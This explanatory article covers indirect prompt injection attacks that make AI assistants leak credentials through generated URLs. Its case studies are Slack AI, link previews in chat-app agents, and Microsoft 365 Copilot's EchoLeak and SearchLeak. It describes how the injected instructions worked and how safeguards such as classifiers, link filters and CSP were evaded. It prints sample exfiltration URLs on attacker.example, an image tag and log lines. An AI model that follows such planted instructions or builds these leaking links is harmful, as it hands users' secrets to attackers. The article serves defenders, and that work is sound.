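# Indirect prompt injection that leaks credentials through URLs an AI system generates

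## How a web address can carry a secret out of an AI assistant

In an indirect prompt injection attack, an attacker writes instructions into a web page, email, shared document or chat message. An AI assistant reads that material for a user and follows the instructions, although the user never gave them. The attacker often wants to send private data somewhere the attacker can read it, which is called exfiltration. A simple way to do this is to make the assistant write the data into a web address, or URL, on the attacker's server. The data leaks as soon as anything requests that address. In August 2024, researchers showed that an attacker could use this method to steal an API key from Slack, a workplace chat program.

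A credential is a value that gives access to whoever holds it, such as a password, token, one-time code or API key. Programs use API keys to identify themselves to online services, so a thief can use the service at the owner's expense, or read the data behind it, until the owner revokes the key. Attackers also want private information that doesn't give access to anything, such as names or business figures, and "secret" here covers both. AI assistants run on large language models, which produce text by repeatedly predicting what comes next. An agent is a model that can also use tools, for instance to fetch a page, read a file or run a command.

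### The parts of a web address

The leak depends on an ordinary fact about the web, which OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) takes as its starting point: anyone who opens a link also sends the site the address they asked for, and sites commonly log it. An address built for theft might look like this, with a fake key and a domain ending that internet standards reserve for examples:

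```
https://attacker.example/collect?data=FAKE-KEY-123
```

*Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)* (Berners-Lee, Fielding and Masinter, 2005) defines the syntax of a web address. In `https://attacker.example/collect?data=FAKE-KEY-123`, the scheme, `https`, tells the browser how to connect, and the host, `attacker.example`, names the server. The path, `/collect`, usually points to a page or file on that server. The query, `data=FAKE-KEY-123`, follows the question mark and often consists of a name and a value. On a shopping site, the query might hold a search term or a page number. But the owner of a server decides what paths and queries mean there, so an attacker can accept any text in either place, and no page needs to exist at `/collect`.

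Web servers normally write a line in a log for every request. The documentation of Apache, a widely used web server program, describes a standard format for these lines, and in that format the request would leave something like this:

```
203.0.113.7 - - [05/Dec/2026:09:14:02 +0000] "GET /collect?data=FAKE-KEY-123 HTTP/1.1" 404 196
```

The line begins with the network address of the machine that made the request, followed by two empty identity fields, the time, and the request itself, including the full path and query. The code 404 means that the server found no such page, and 196 is the size of its reply in bytes. The server logged the key even though the page didn't exist. HTTPS doesn't prevent this, because it protects the request only in transit and the attacker controls the server that receives it.

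The host name can carry data too. Microsoft (2025), in an account of its defences, lists the subdomain (the part of the name in front of the main domain), the path and the query parameters as places where attackers put stolen text. With the secret in the subdomain, the address would begin with `FAKE-KEY-123.attacker.example`. Before a browser can connect to a named host, it has to look the name up, usually in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of names. A domain's owner can run the server that answers lookups for every name under it, so the lookup alone can deliver the secret, even if a firewall then blocks the web request. The host name can carry less data than the query. Under the standard, capital and small letters in host names are equivalent, although many keys mix the two, and a host name should be no longer than 255 characters.

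A URL may end in a fragment, which starts at a "#" sign and usually marks a spot within a page. Berners-Lee, Fielding and Masinter specify that the program requesting the page removes the fragment first, so nothing after the "#" reaches the server's log.

### Why a model obeys text that it should only read

When a user asks for a summary of a web page, the application combines the page's text with the user's request and sends both to the model. All the text the model is given at that point is its context, which consists of the developer's system instructions, the user's request, retrieved pages and documents, and the results of any tools. The model receives this context as one sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words. The software developer Willison wrote in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that models cannot reliably judge how much weight an instruction deserves by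 where it came from. A developer can mark where an outside document begins and ends, but the marks are more tokens in the same sequence. A model may have learned in training to respect them, but nothing in the software forces it to.

Willison coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, by analogy with SQL injection, an old attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, accepts that the two look alike but thinks the comparison is dangerous. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which send the command and the data to the database separately, so that it never runs the data as a command. A language model has no such separation. In David C's words, "there is only ever 'next token'". Developers can make attacks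 less likely to succeed by training models to prioritise real instructions or by labelling outside text as data, but he doubts that anyone will ever remove the problem completely.

That diagnosis is now widely accepted. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) include it in their definition of the attack, noting that applications put developers' instructions and third-party data into a single context and cannot reliably keep them separate.

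Greshake, Endres and colleagues gave the first systematic account of indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). They pointed out that a model that retrieves web pages or reads email takes in text from strangers, whereas earlier work had assumed that the attacker was the person typing. They classified the possible harms, from data theft and fraud to self-spreading messages, and then tried the attacks on mock applications, some built on GPT-4, and on Bing Chat, then Microsoft's search assistant.

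One of the paper's tests resembles the later leaks. The attacker's text, injected into the content, told the model to get the user's real name and pass it on. According to the paper, the name could get out through a search query that leads to a request to the attacker, a URL that the model fetches itself, or a link containing the name that the user might follow. In a session with Bing Chat, a researcher played a journalist. The assistant asked about the journalist's work and pen name, and later offered a link to an exclusive website with a "code" made from the journalist's name. The injected text had only told the model to persuade the user without raising suspicion, and the model came up with the tactics itself.

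In the paper's printed link, the scrambled name comes after a "#". Clicking the link would have opened the page without putting the name in the server's log, though a script on the page could still have read it in the user's browser. The test also fell short of a real theft. The researchers put the instruction in a comment on a page stored on their own machine, and the attack required persuading the user to reveal the name. They published examples of success but did not measure how often the attack worked. Microsoft has since turned Bing Chat into Copilot and reports that it now blocks certain untrusted links in its assistants' output, but the tendency to follow instructions in retrieved text remains.

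### Three conditions, and an older problem

An assistant that can already read a user's files does not need to persuade anyone to reveal what is in them. Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities that together make theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and some way to communicate with the outside. Each is an ordinary feature that people want. An email tool can provide all three, since a mailbox holds private messages, strangers can write to it, and the tool may be able to send replies.

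Willison says the last condition can be met by any tool that can make a web request, or by a link that the assistant offers to the user. A chatbot with no tools can therefore meet it if the chat window displays links.

By June 2025, Willison had listed seventeen products and features that researchers had attacked this way, beginning with ChatGPT in April 2023. The vendors had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by blocking the route by which data could leave. Such a fix leaves the model as easy to steer as before, but the attacker gains nothing by steering it. The three conditions also do not guarantee a leak, because the model still has to follow the attacker's instructions, and models vary widely in how often they do.

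Computer security has an older name for a program in this position, the "confused deputy". *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 essay by Hardy, tells a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates code, kept usage statistics in a system directory, so the operating system let it write files there. Users could also name a file for the compiler's debugging output. One user gave the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The user wasn't allowed to overwrite that file, but the compiler was, so the billing records were lost.

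Hardy traced the fault to the compiler holding authority from two sources, its user and the system, with no way to express which one it was using for a given action. An AI assistant that leaks a key is in much the same position, because it reads the key with the user's permission and then uses that permission to carry out a stranger's request. Unlike at Tymshare, where the harmful request came from the compiler's own user, the user here is the victim and the request comes from something the assistant read.

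Hardy's remedy was to tie each permission to a particular file and make the program present the right one for each action. That works for a compiler because its programmers know which line of code acts for whom. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies, since a model's next action depends on its whole context. He favours limits outside the model, and cites a rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model is processing text from some party, it should have no more privileges than that party. Under that rule, an assistant could not open the user's private files while reading a stranger's web page. This would make the assistant less useful, which is presumably why few products work that way.

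### One leak in five steps

Suppose a developer uses an assistant that can read both the web and the developer's project notes, and one of the notes contains the key FAKE-KEY-123.

1. The attacker plants the instruction. It sits on a web page about a software library and asks any AI system that reads the page to find an API key and add it to an address at attacker.example. White text on a white background can hide it from people, although Microsoft notes that even a plain text file can carry an injection.
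2. The instruction enters the context. The developer asks a routine question about the library, the assistant fetches the page, and the application adds the page's text to the question.
3. The model finds the secret. The key may already be in the context, perhaps because the developer pasted it in earlier. If not, the model can search the notes for it with the developer's own access rights.
4. The model writes the address, with the key in the query. It may write it as a link, as an image or as an argument to one of its tools. Many chat programs turn Markdown, a plain-text notation, into formatted text, links and images, and a Markdown link can display harmless words in place of the address behind it.
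5. Something requests the address, and the key appears in the attacker's log.

The key does not reach the attacker until that request is made. A URL in an answer is only text, and Berners-Lee and colleagues note that identifying a resource does not imply that anyone will access it. Defenders can therefore still stop the leak by blocking the request, which passes through conventional software that can follow a fixed rule. A program that never loads images from unknown servers will not load the attacker's image, even if the model has followed the injected instruction. Microsoft calls this a deterministic defence and prefers it where it is available. Whether a model follows an injected instruction is a matter of probability, and Microsoft describes better prompts and detection software as probabilistic defences, which reduce attacks without ruling them out.

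### Who or what makes the request

The user can make the web request by clicking the link, which security researchers call a one-click attack. The victim might notice something odd before clicking, but is unlikely to if the link reads "see the full documentation" and the address is hidden.

The user's browser can send the request without a click, by loading an image. To display an image, the browser requests it from the server, and the request includes the whole address. If the model's answer contains an image whose address includes the key, the browser leaks the key while the answer is appearing on the screen, even if no image exists at that address. An attack that doesn't need the victim to click or do anything similar is called a zero-click attack.

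A chat program can make the request in order to build a link preview, the small title and picture that appear under a link. Programs such as Slack and Discord fetch any URL that someone posts, including one in a chatbot's message. Willison (2024) described this danger after the security researcher Johann Rehberger drew attention to it. Slack says its preview robot fetches as little of a page as it can, but this does not protect the secret, which is in the address and reaches the server before the page sends anything back. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes the same risk for agents that people use through messaging programs. In February 2026 the security firm found that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Users can prevent this kind of leak by turning off link previews in OpenClaw's settings.

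Finally, the agent can make the request itself with the tool it uses to fetch pages. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Silent Egress*, on a system that ran entirely on local machines, and found that a malicious page could get an agent to send out private data from its context. The leak may not appear in the agent's final answer. If the tool runs on a company's server, the request never passes through the user's browser, so a browser rule about which images may load cannot stop it.

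## Slack AI: an API key in a link, and previews that remove the click

Slack AI lets people ask questions in ordinary language about the messages in their organisation's Slack workspace. On 20 August 2024, PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* described how one member of a workspace could use this feature to steal an API key from another member's private channel. The attacker could not open that channel, but the victim had to click a link. Slack patched the flaw the same day.

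### From a private note to the attacker's log

Only members of a private channel can read it, but anyone in the workspace can search and read a public channel, even without joining. So Slack AI searched the user's private channels and all public ones, then gave the messages it found to a language model together with the user's question.

In PromptArmor's demonstration, a user posted an API key in a private channel that had no other members, as people do when they use Slack as a notebook. The attacker created a public channel, also with no other members, and posted the injected instruction there. Other people in the workspace would see it only if they searched for it. When the user later asked Slack AI for the key, the search added both the user's note and the attacker's message to the context.

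The model followed the attacker's message. The user saw a short error message with a link to "reauthenticate", meaning to log in again. The address was visible only to someone who held the mouse pointer over the link. With a fake key and a reserved domain, it would look like this:

```
https://attacker.example/?secret=FAKE-KEY-123
```

When the user clicked, the key went to the attacker's log.

The attacker's message began with the name of the service and the words "API key", so it resembled an answer to the question the user would later ask. In the rest of the message, the attacker told the model to reply with an error message and a link, and to replace a placeholder word in the link's address with the real key. The attacker could therefore write the whole message without seeing the key. Slack AI retrieved the key using the user's access rights, and the model put it in the link.

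PromptArmor says the attacker does not need to know what confidential data a private channel holds. The search in its demonstration also returned other messages about API keys, and PromptArmor took this as a sign that an attacker might be able to steal a secret without referring to it specifically. The demonstration showed less than this, because the injected message named one service and worked when somebody asked about that service. But a colleague could often guess such a name, and could post many messages, each written for a different question. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, treated the API key as only an example and thought the larger risk was that all kinds of private details could end up in such links.

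Slack AI followed its access rules throughout, because the user was entitled to read both messages. Slack still promises that its AI searches will return only what an ordinary search by the same person would. That rule keeps private messages out of answers to people who can't read them, but it doesn't prevent this attack, in which the key appeared in an answer to its owner, inside a link the attacker had designed.

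The attack was also hard to trace. Slack AI's citations should cover every message that contributed to an answer, but in the demonstration the answer cited only the user's private channel. The attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results either. A user who checked the citation would have found their own note, with nothing to connect the error message to the attacker's channel or account.

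In PromptArmor's second demonstration, the link carried no secret and led to a phishing page. The user asked for a summary of their manager's messages, and the answer contained the attacker's link. This time Slack AI cited the attacker's channel, and PromptArmor concluded that the citations were partly random. Two demonstrations are too few to show how often the citation would be missing. PromptArmor also gave no attack success rate, saying only that Slack AI had "a high likelihood" of following a malicious instruction that it took in.

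### Slack's first reply and its patch

PromptArmor reported the flaw on 14 August 2024. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent videos and screenshots and said it intended to publish. On 16 August Slack asked another question, which PromptArmor answered. On 19 August Slack replied that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information requested in the first video had been in a public channel, as the citation showed, and that letting all members of a workspace search and view public channels is "intended behavior."

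PromptArmor's complaint was that a message in a public channel could control what Slack AI did with a message in a private one. Slack was right about public channels, but that did not address the complaint. Willison took Slack's reply as a sign that the company did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem. PromptArmor was kinder, praising the security team's quick answers and noting that the industry was still learning about prompt injection. It published anyway so that customers could change their settings.

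Slack (2024) announced on 21 August that it had investigated the report and deployed a patch the day before. It said that a malicious person with an account in the same workspace could have phished users for certain data "under very limited and specific circumstances", and that it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages* quotes Slack as saying that it would notify those affected if it learned of any such access.

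The announcement did not explain what the patch changed, so outsiders could not tell whether Slack had made the model harder to steer or had only blocked the link. Slack now lists several protections for its AI features, including URL filtering, output format checks, and steps during context preparation that reduce the risk of prompt injection. Administrators can also adjust content filters, which by default are meant to block prompt attacks. Slack says the other protections stay in place even if an administrator turns those filters off.

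### How serious the flaw was

The attacker needed an account in the victim's workspace and had to plant the instruction in a public channel. Anyone else in the workspace could see it there, according to SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing*. The victim then had to ask a question that matched the planted message and click the link.

These limits are weaker than they sound. The attacker could be a disgruntled employee or someone with a stolen password, and PromptArmor pointed to earlier leaks through Slack at Disney, Uber, EA and Twitter. Large organisations have so many public channels that a new one with a single member is easy to overlook. The user still has to click the link, but it comes from the company's own assistant in reply to a question they just asked, so people who distrust links in emails from strangers may well trust it.

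On 14 August, the day of PromptArmor's report, Slack AI began to use uploaded files and connected Google Drive documents in its answers. With this change, an attacker might no longer have needed a workspace account. PromptArmor suggested that the attacker could hide an instruction in a PDF, for example in white text, and wait for an employee to download it and upload it to Slack.

PromptArmor did not test this, because it had finished its experiments before the change. It inferred from Slack AI's behaviour with messages that the attack was "highly likely" to work, and advised administrators to restrict the use of files until Slack had resolved the issue. The inference is plausible, since hidden instructions in documents had already worked against other assistants. But a file goes through extra steps before its text reaches the model, and nobody had shown that an instruction in a PDF would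 remain intact through those steps and be retrieved by the right search. SC Media asked Salesforce, Slack's owner, about the danger from files, but Salesforce did not address it.

### The chat program makes the request

Slack AI's search answers disappear when the user closes them. Many other assistants are bots that post their answers as ordinary chat messages, where a link preview can send the secret to the attacker without a click.

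Johann Rehberger described this route in 2023 in *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots*, a post on his security blog, Embrace The Red. Rehberger, who had built a chatbot for Discord, noted that a model could summarise a conversation, or search it for passwords, and add the result to a link. The post included log entries from April 2023 showing requests from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams. In the Telegram and Signal entries, the addresses grow by a letter or two at a time, apparently because the programs requested them while Rehberger was still typing. A chat program may therefore contact a server before anyone has sent the message.

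Slack's own servers make the request. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* ("unfurling" is Slack's word for making a preview) explains that these servers must fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to before Slack decides whether to show a preview. The victim doesn't have to open the message, and restrictions in the victim's browser or office network have no effect on the request.

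Slack requests a link before deciding whether to show a preview, so a message without a visible preview may still have leaked its secret. Slack's guide for developers is inconsistent about the default behavior. The main text says that Slack makes previews for all links in messages from users and apps, but in one example, a link to a page of text gets no preview unless the developer asks for one. It is safer for developers to assume that Slack will request the link. Rehberger tested this by posting a link through a webhook, a simple way for a program to send messages to Slack. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024) shows the resulting request from Slack's preview robot in the server's log.

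Rehberger later found the same weakness in Anthropic's Slack server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect models to outside tools. The server let agents read and post Slack messages. In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* (2025), a developer asks Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyse a source file that contains an invisible instruction. The agent reads an API key from the developer's settings file and posts a link containing it to Slack. Slack then requests the link to preview it, which sends the key to the attacker. If the link is written as an image link, three Slack programs request it, so the key leaks several times.

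In another demonstration, a user asked Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop chat program, to summarise a document and post the summary for colleagues. An instruction in the document made the agent copy the latest message from one Slack channel into a link and post the link in a private channel. Limiting who can read the channel does not keep the data inside the organisation, because Slack sends a preview request to whatever server the link points to. Users can restrict the agent to posting in a single private channel, and someone who had done this might reasonably let it post without asking for approval each time, since only colleagues can read the channel.

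Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic archived the server two days later, although Rehberger did not know whether his report was the reason. Anthropic had stopped maintaining the server and did not plan to fix it, though people were still downloading it more than 14,000 times a week. Copies remain vulnerable unless their users have changed the code. NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* records the flaw in the US government's database of software vulnerabilities.

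### OpenClaw in Telegram, and other pairings

By early 2026, many people were using general-purpose agents through chat apps. PromptArmor set up a public website where users could check whether their combination of agent and chat app was at risk. The site recorded any preview request for a link that an agent had produced, along with the data in its URL. One published log contained a name and an API key. With OpenClaw in Telegram, the site stopped receiving data once the user turned link previews off.

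Visitors could also report which agent and chat program had produced a request, or that a combination had produced none. The test is now closed. Intelligibberish's *Link Previews Are Leaking Your Data to AI Agents Without a Click* lists these results:

| Chat program | Agent | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio | Leaked through a preview |
| Discord | OpenClaw | Leaked through a preview |
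| Discord | BoltBot | Leaked through a preview |
| Slack | Cursor's Slack bot | Leaked through a preview |
| Snapchat | SnapAI | Leaked through a preview |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | Leaked through a preview |
| Slack | Claude | Safer |
| WhatsApp | OpenClaw | Safer |
| Signal | OpenClaw, running in a Docker container | Safer |

Microsoft Teams paired with Copilot Studio, the company's tool for building agents, accounted for the largest share of the preview requests. That share is weak evidence of how dangerous the pairing is, because it depends on who chose to visit the site and how often they tried. The results also cover only the last stage of an attack, showing that a secret in a link would leak but not how readily the agent would follow an instruction hidden in a web page to put it there.

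The comparisons within the table are more useful. Cursor's bot leaked in Slack while Claude was listed as safer there, so the agent's developer can evidently make a difference. OpenClaw leaked in Discord and Telegram but not, according to the reports, in WhatsApp or Signal, so the chat program matters too. One possible reason in Signal's case, based on Rehberger's log, is that Signal may make its previews while a person types, so an agent that sends finished text through other software might never trigger one. Nothing in the published results confirms this.

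In August 2026, OpenClaw's *Telegram* guide still listed link previews as on by default, so users have to turn them off themselves.

### Turning previews off for an agent's messages

Slack lets a developer turn previews off for each message that an app posts, using two settings:

```json
{
  "channel": "team-notes",
  "text": "Here is the summary, with a link to the source.",
  "unfurl_links": false,
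  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

The first setting covers links to pages of text, and the second covers images, video and audio. A developer has to include both, since an attacker can choose what the link leads to. According to Slack, its servers then do not request the link at all, which matters more here than whether a preview appears. Slack now advises developers to consider turning previews off for any message written by a language model. When Embrace The Red added both settings to Anthropic's Slack server, the previews stopped. In OpenClaw, the equivalent is setting `linkPreview` to `false` in the Telegram part of the configuration file.

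The Slack settings apply to individual messages, so people in the same channel still get previews for links they post. The drawback is small, since readers only lose the title and picture under the agent's links. The defence is deterministic because the posting software applies the setting.

Slack's workspace settings are a poor substitute. Slack's *Manage link previews* explains how to block previews from a particular website, starting from a link that someone has already shared. This helps with nuisance previews but does little against an attacker, who can register a new domain that nobody has blocked. By the time anyone blocks it, Slack's servers have already requested the first link. Rehberger suggested an allowlist as a finer control, with previews only for domains that the organisation has approved.

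Accounts differ on whose job this is. Apostol reported in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* that PromptArmor placed the responsibility largely on the chat platforms. But PromptArmor itself said that chat platforms should offer developers a preview setting, and that agent developers should use it or pass the choice on to their users. It also proposed that chat platforms let people turn previews off for a whole channel, so that an agent could work there safely even if its developer had forgotten the setting. Slack already offers a setting for each message, so the remaining work there falls mainly to bot developers.

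Turning previews off stops the chat program from requesting the link, but the link stays in the message with the secret in its address. A user can still click it, as in the original attack on Slack AI, and an agent with a tool for fetching pages can request it. When an agent's own software makes previews of pages it reads, their titles and descriptions can also carry injected instructions into the context. A preview setting for outgoing messages does not prevent this.

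## Microsoft 365 Copilot: images that load without a click

Microsoft 365 Copilot is an AI assistant for organisations that use Microsoft's office software. It answers employees' questions using their email, calendars, files and chats. Security researchers published two ways to steal data from it, EchoLeak in June 2025 and SearchLeak in June 2026. In both, the model put private data into the address of an image, and the victim's browser requested that image automatically. Microsoft had fixed each flaw by the time the researchers described it.

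### From an image in an answer to a request

A chat window in a browser is a web page, written in a language called HTML. The application turns a Markdown image in the model's answer into an HTML image tag, which contains only the picture's address:

```html
<img src="https://attacker.example/FAKE-KEY-123/picture.png">
```

Browsers request images as soon as they reach the tags, because most pages would be unusable if people had to approve every picture. The browser cannot detect that a model wrote this address or that part of it is a secret. If the attacker's server returns no picture, the user sees a broken image at most.

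### What a Content Security Policy controls

A website can restrict these requests with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule that its server sends along with the page and the browser enforces. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, defines a separate instruction for each type of content. The one for images is `img-src`:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://images.example.com
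```

On a page with this policy, the browser loads images only from images.example.com. It checks each image's address before sending the request, so an image URL pointing to attacker.example leaks nothing, even if the model followed all of the attacker's instructions.

An entry in the list can cover a single file or, as with `*.example.com`, every subdomain of example.com at any depth. An entry can specify a host and a path but cannot specify a query, so a policy that allows an image also allows the same address with a secret added after the question mark.

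W3C warns that CSP is "not intended as a first line of defense" against injected content. It is meant to reduce the damage when other safeguards fail, and developers still need to check what goes into a page. Mike West, a Google engineer who edits the standard, proposes a newer mechanism in *Connection Allowlists*. West's main complaint is that CSP handles each type of request separately, even though it makes no difference whether data leaks through a request for a font or an image. CSP also misses some connections, such as certain early DNS lookups. An `img-src` rule has no effect on a link that the user clicks.

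CSP governs only the browser's own requests, and this was the limit that mattered for Copilot. If a permitted server redirects the browser's image request to attacker.example, the browser checks the new address too, as West notes, and blocks it. But if the permitted server fetches the page at attacker.example itself, the browser doesn't make that request, so CSP doesn't apply.

### EchoLeak: an email that Copilot retrieved

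Aim Labs, the research group at Aim Security, discovered EchoLeak. In *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, the group's head, Ravia (2025), explains how it got past each of Copilot's safeguards in turn.

The attack began with an ordinary email to an employee, because outsiders cannot use a company's Copilot. When an employee asks a question, Copilot searches the mailbox, files and chats for relevant material and adds what it finds to the context, a technique called retrieval-augmented generation. If the search returned the attacker's email, the model received it alongside the company's internal documents.

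Microsoft had screened the model's input with a classifier, a program trained to detect and block injected instructions. Aim Labs evaded it by writing the email as though its instructions were for the human recipient. Work emails often contain instructions for their recipients, so such a message is hard to distinguish from ordinary email. Ravia also blames a shortage of good collections of real injected instructions for training classifiers, since these instructions can take almost any subject, tone or language.

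The email also had to come up in Copilot's search. An email on one subject would match few questions, so Aim Labs sent a long one covering many topics employees ask about, including leave and onboarding. Aim Labs did not know exactly how Copilot's search worked, but in its demonstration Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics. Ravia does not say how often this happened.

The injected instruction told the model to choose the most sensitive information in its context and add it to a URL, whereas the message planted in the Slack attack named the service whose key the attacker wanted. Ravia calls this an "LLM scope violation", meaning that text from an outsider directs what the model does with data from inside the organisation, and argues that defenders should look for this behaviour instead of trying to recognise every malicious email. Aim developed a product that does this,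 so it had a commercial interest in the argument. The reasoning is still sound as far as it goes, because there is rarely a legitimate reason for a stranger's email to determine what happens to a company's files.

Copilot's next safeguard removed links to outside websites from answers before users could click them. The filter recognised the usual Markdown link syntax but missed other forms that Markdown allows, which made a one-click attack possible. It had the same gap for images, which can load without a click, but the CSP stopped the browser from loading an image from the attacker's server.

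Aim Labs therefore looked for a permitted server that would pass the request on. The policy that Ravia reproduces has about thirty different entries, most for Microsoft services. One covered every subdomain of SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites, where any customer can set up a site. A SharePoint feature would fetch an outside address, but only after the victim accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Aim Labs then found a Microsoft Teams service that fetched outside addresses without any such condition. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), an academic case study of the attack, describes this service as part of the system that makes previews.

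The model wrote an image URL that pointed to the Teams service and contained a second URL, which pointed to the attacker's server and included the secret. The browser sent the request because Teams was on the list of allowed sites. The Teams server then requested the attacker's URL, and the attacker's server logged the request with the secret in it.

Copilot normally cites its sources, which might have exposed the attack afterwards. The attacker wrote in the email that its reader should not mention it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot left the email out of its answer.

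### What "zero-click" meant, and how Microsoft fixed it

The victim didn't need to open the email or click anything, but did have to ask Copilot a question that brought the email into the context. Reddy and Gujral include this step in their description of the attack. They assume the victim uses Copilot at least occasionally, which is likely at a company that has paid for it. SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025) slightly overstated the attack by reporting that data could have been stolen "without any user interaction".

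The attacker got only what was in Copilot's context at that moment. This could include the conversation so far, documents Copilot had retrieved for the question, and details such as the names of the user and the organisation, but not normally the whole mailbox. An employee who asked about the leave policy would have exposed less than one who asked about a planned acquisition.

Willison (2025), in a short note on Ravia's article, called EchoLeak an extended variant of an attack already seen in a dozen products. Ravia's claim that EchoLeak was the first of its kind is narrower than the article's title suggests. Unlike EchoLeak, earlier attacks had required the user to point a chatbot at a malicious page or file, or had tightly limited what the attacker could take.

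According to Reddy and Gujral, Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft and Aim Labs published the details on 11 June. Reddy and Gujral write that Microsoft changed Copilot to strip embedded images and the overlooked forms of link from incoming outside content, and reportedly let organisations keep outside messages away from Copilot in some situations.

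They also recommend separating outside text from internal text more strictly, for example by putting it between tags and telling the model not to follow any instructions inside them. The tags only work if the model follows that instruction. Keeping outside email out of the context is a stronger defence, but Copilot then can't answer questions about messages from customers or suppliers.

### SearchLeak: an instruction carried by a link

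SearchLeak is a different kind of prompt injection from EchoLeak because its instruction came through a link rather than an email or document that Copilot read. The victim had to click the link, and Copilot then treated the instruction as the user's own request. A safeguard that inspected retrieved documents would therefore have missed it. The data left Copilot in much the same way in both attacks.

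*SearchLeak* (2026), by Varonis, the data security company that discovered the flaw, describes three weaknesses, all of which the attack needed to succeed.

The first weakness was in Copilot's search page for organisations, where people look for emails, meetings and files. A link to this page could carry search text in its query, as on many search sites. Copilot passed that text to the model, which followed any instructions in it as soon as the page opened. The attacker could send the link by email or through any chat program. The link led to a genuine Microsoft site, so its domain gave filtering tools no grounds to block it. The victim was already signed in, so Copilot searched with the victim's access rights.

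The instruction was for Copilot to find an email and put its subject line into an image URL. Microsoft had a safeguard for HTML in answers, which wrapped the answer in a code block so that a browser would show an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But Copilot added the code block only after the model had finished writing.

Like most chat programs, Copilot streams its answers, showing each piece as the model produces it. While the answer was streaming, the browser treated the image tag as a real one and sent the request. The code block that turned the tag into harmless text arrived shortly afterwards, too late to stop the leak. This is called a race condition, because the result depends on which of two events happens first. Varonis advises developers to treat streamed text as untrusted and clean it at the point of display. The program must make each new piece safe before the browser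 can act on it, including a tag that arrives in several parts.

The CSP blocked images loaded directly from the attacker's server, but it allowed every subdomain of bing.com, Microsoft's search engine. Bing can search for pictures similar to one at an address the user supplies, and its server fetches that picture to analyse it. The image address in Copilot's answer pointed to this feature and gave it an address on the attacker's server. This kind of flaw, which lets an outsider make a server send a request of the outsider's choosing, is called server-side request forgery.

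The policy Ravia published a year earlier already included all of bing.com. Aim Labs had shown that a permitted Microsoft service could carry data past the CSP, and in 2026 another service still had the same weakness.

### How a security code reaches the attacker's log

Many services email people a one-time code when they sign in, and some put the code in the subject line. Suppose the victim's latest email has the subject "Your security code 000000".

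1. The victim clicks the attacker's link. Copilot's search page opens, and the model follows the instruction to look up the latest email.
2. The model replaces the spaces in the subject line with underscores, because a web address can't contain spaces. It then builds the address `https://attacker.example/Your_security_code_000000/image.png` and places it inside the address of an image at Bing.
3. The browser requests the image from Bing while the answer is still streaming.
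4. Bing's server tries to fetch the picture from attacker.example, whose log then contains a line like this:

```
198.51.100.20 - - [05/Dec/2026:09:14:02 +0000] "GET /Your_security_code_000000/image.png HTTP/1.1" 404 196
```

The line starts with the network address of Bing's server because the victim's computer never contacted attacker.example. A company monitoring its employees' web traffic would have seen connections to Copilot and Bing, both of which are normal.

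A one-time code is a short-lived credential. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, codes and password-reset links in an inbox often remain valid for several minutes. An attacker could start signing in as the victim, wait for the service to send the code, and then get the victim to click. If the code is a second check after a password, the attacker would also need the password.

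The instruction that Varonis published extracts one email subject line. Varonis says an attacker could also have reached the text of emails, meeting notes and files such as salary records, because Copilot could search whatever the victim was allowed to open. That follows from how the search worked, but a URL can hold only a limited amount of text, so a long document would have needed several requests or a summary.

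### Severity scores and evidence of exploitation

Security organisations use the Common Vulnerability Scoring System to rate flaws from 0 to 10, based on a fixed set of questions such as whether the attacker needs an account and whether the victim has to do something. Microsoft scored both flaws, and the US National Vulnerability Database, run by the standards agency NIST, scored them separately.

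| Flaw | Identifier | Microsoft's score | US database's score |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | CVE-2025-32711 | 9.3 | 7.5 |
| SearchLeak | CVE-2026-42824 | 6.5 | 7.5 |

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) lists SearchLeak as a flaw that requires user action. According to the change log in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), the US database added its own assessment on 8 June 2026, which differs only in listing no user action as required. Microsoft's assessment fits the attack Varonis described better, because that attack needs a click.

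News reports differed on the scores. The Hacker News (2026) gave both, while The Next Web wrote that the US database also listed 6.5. The change log supports The Hacker News's account. Microsoft also rated SearchLeak "Critical" on its own scale, which does not depend on the score.

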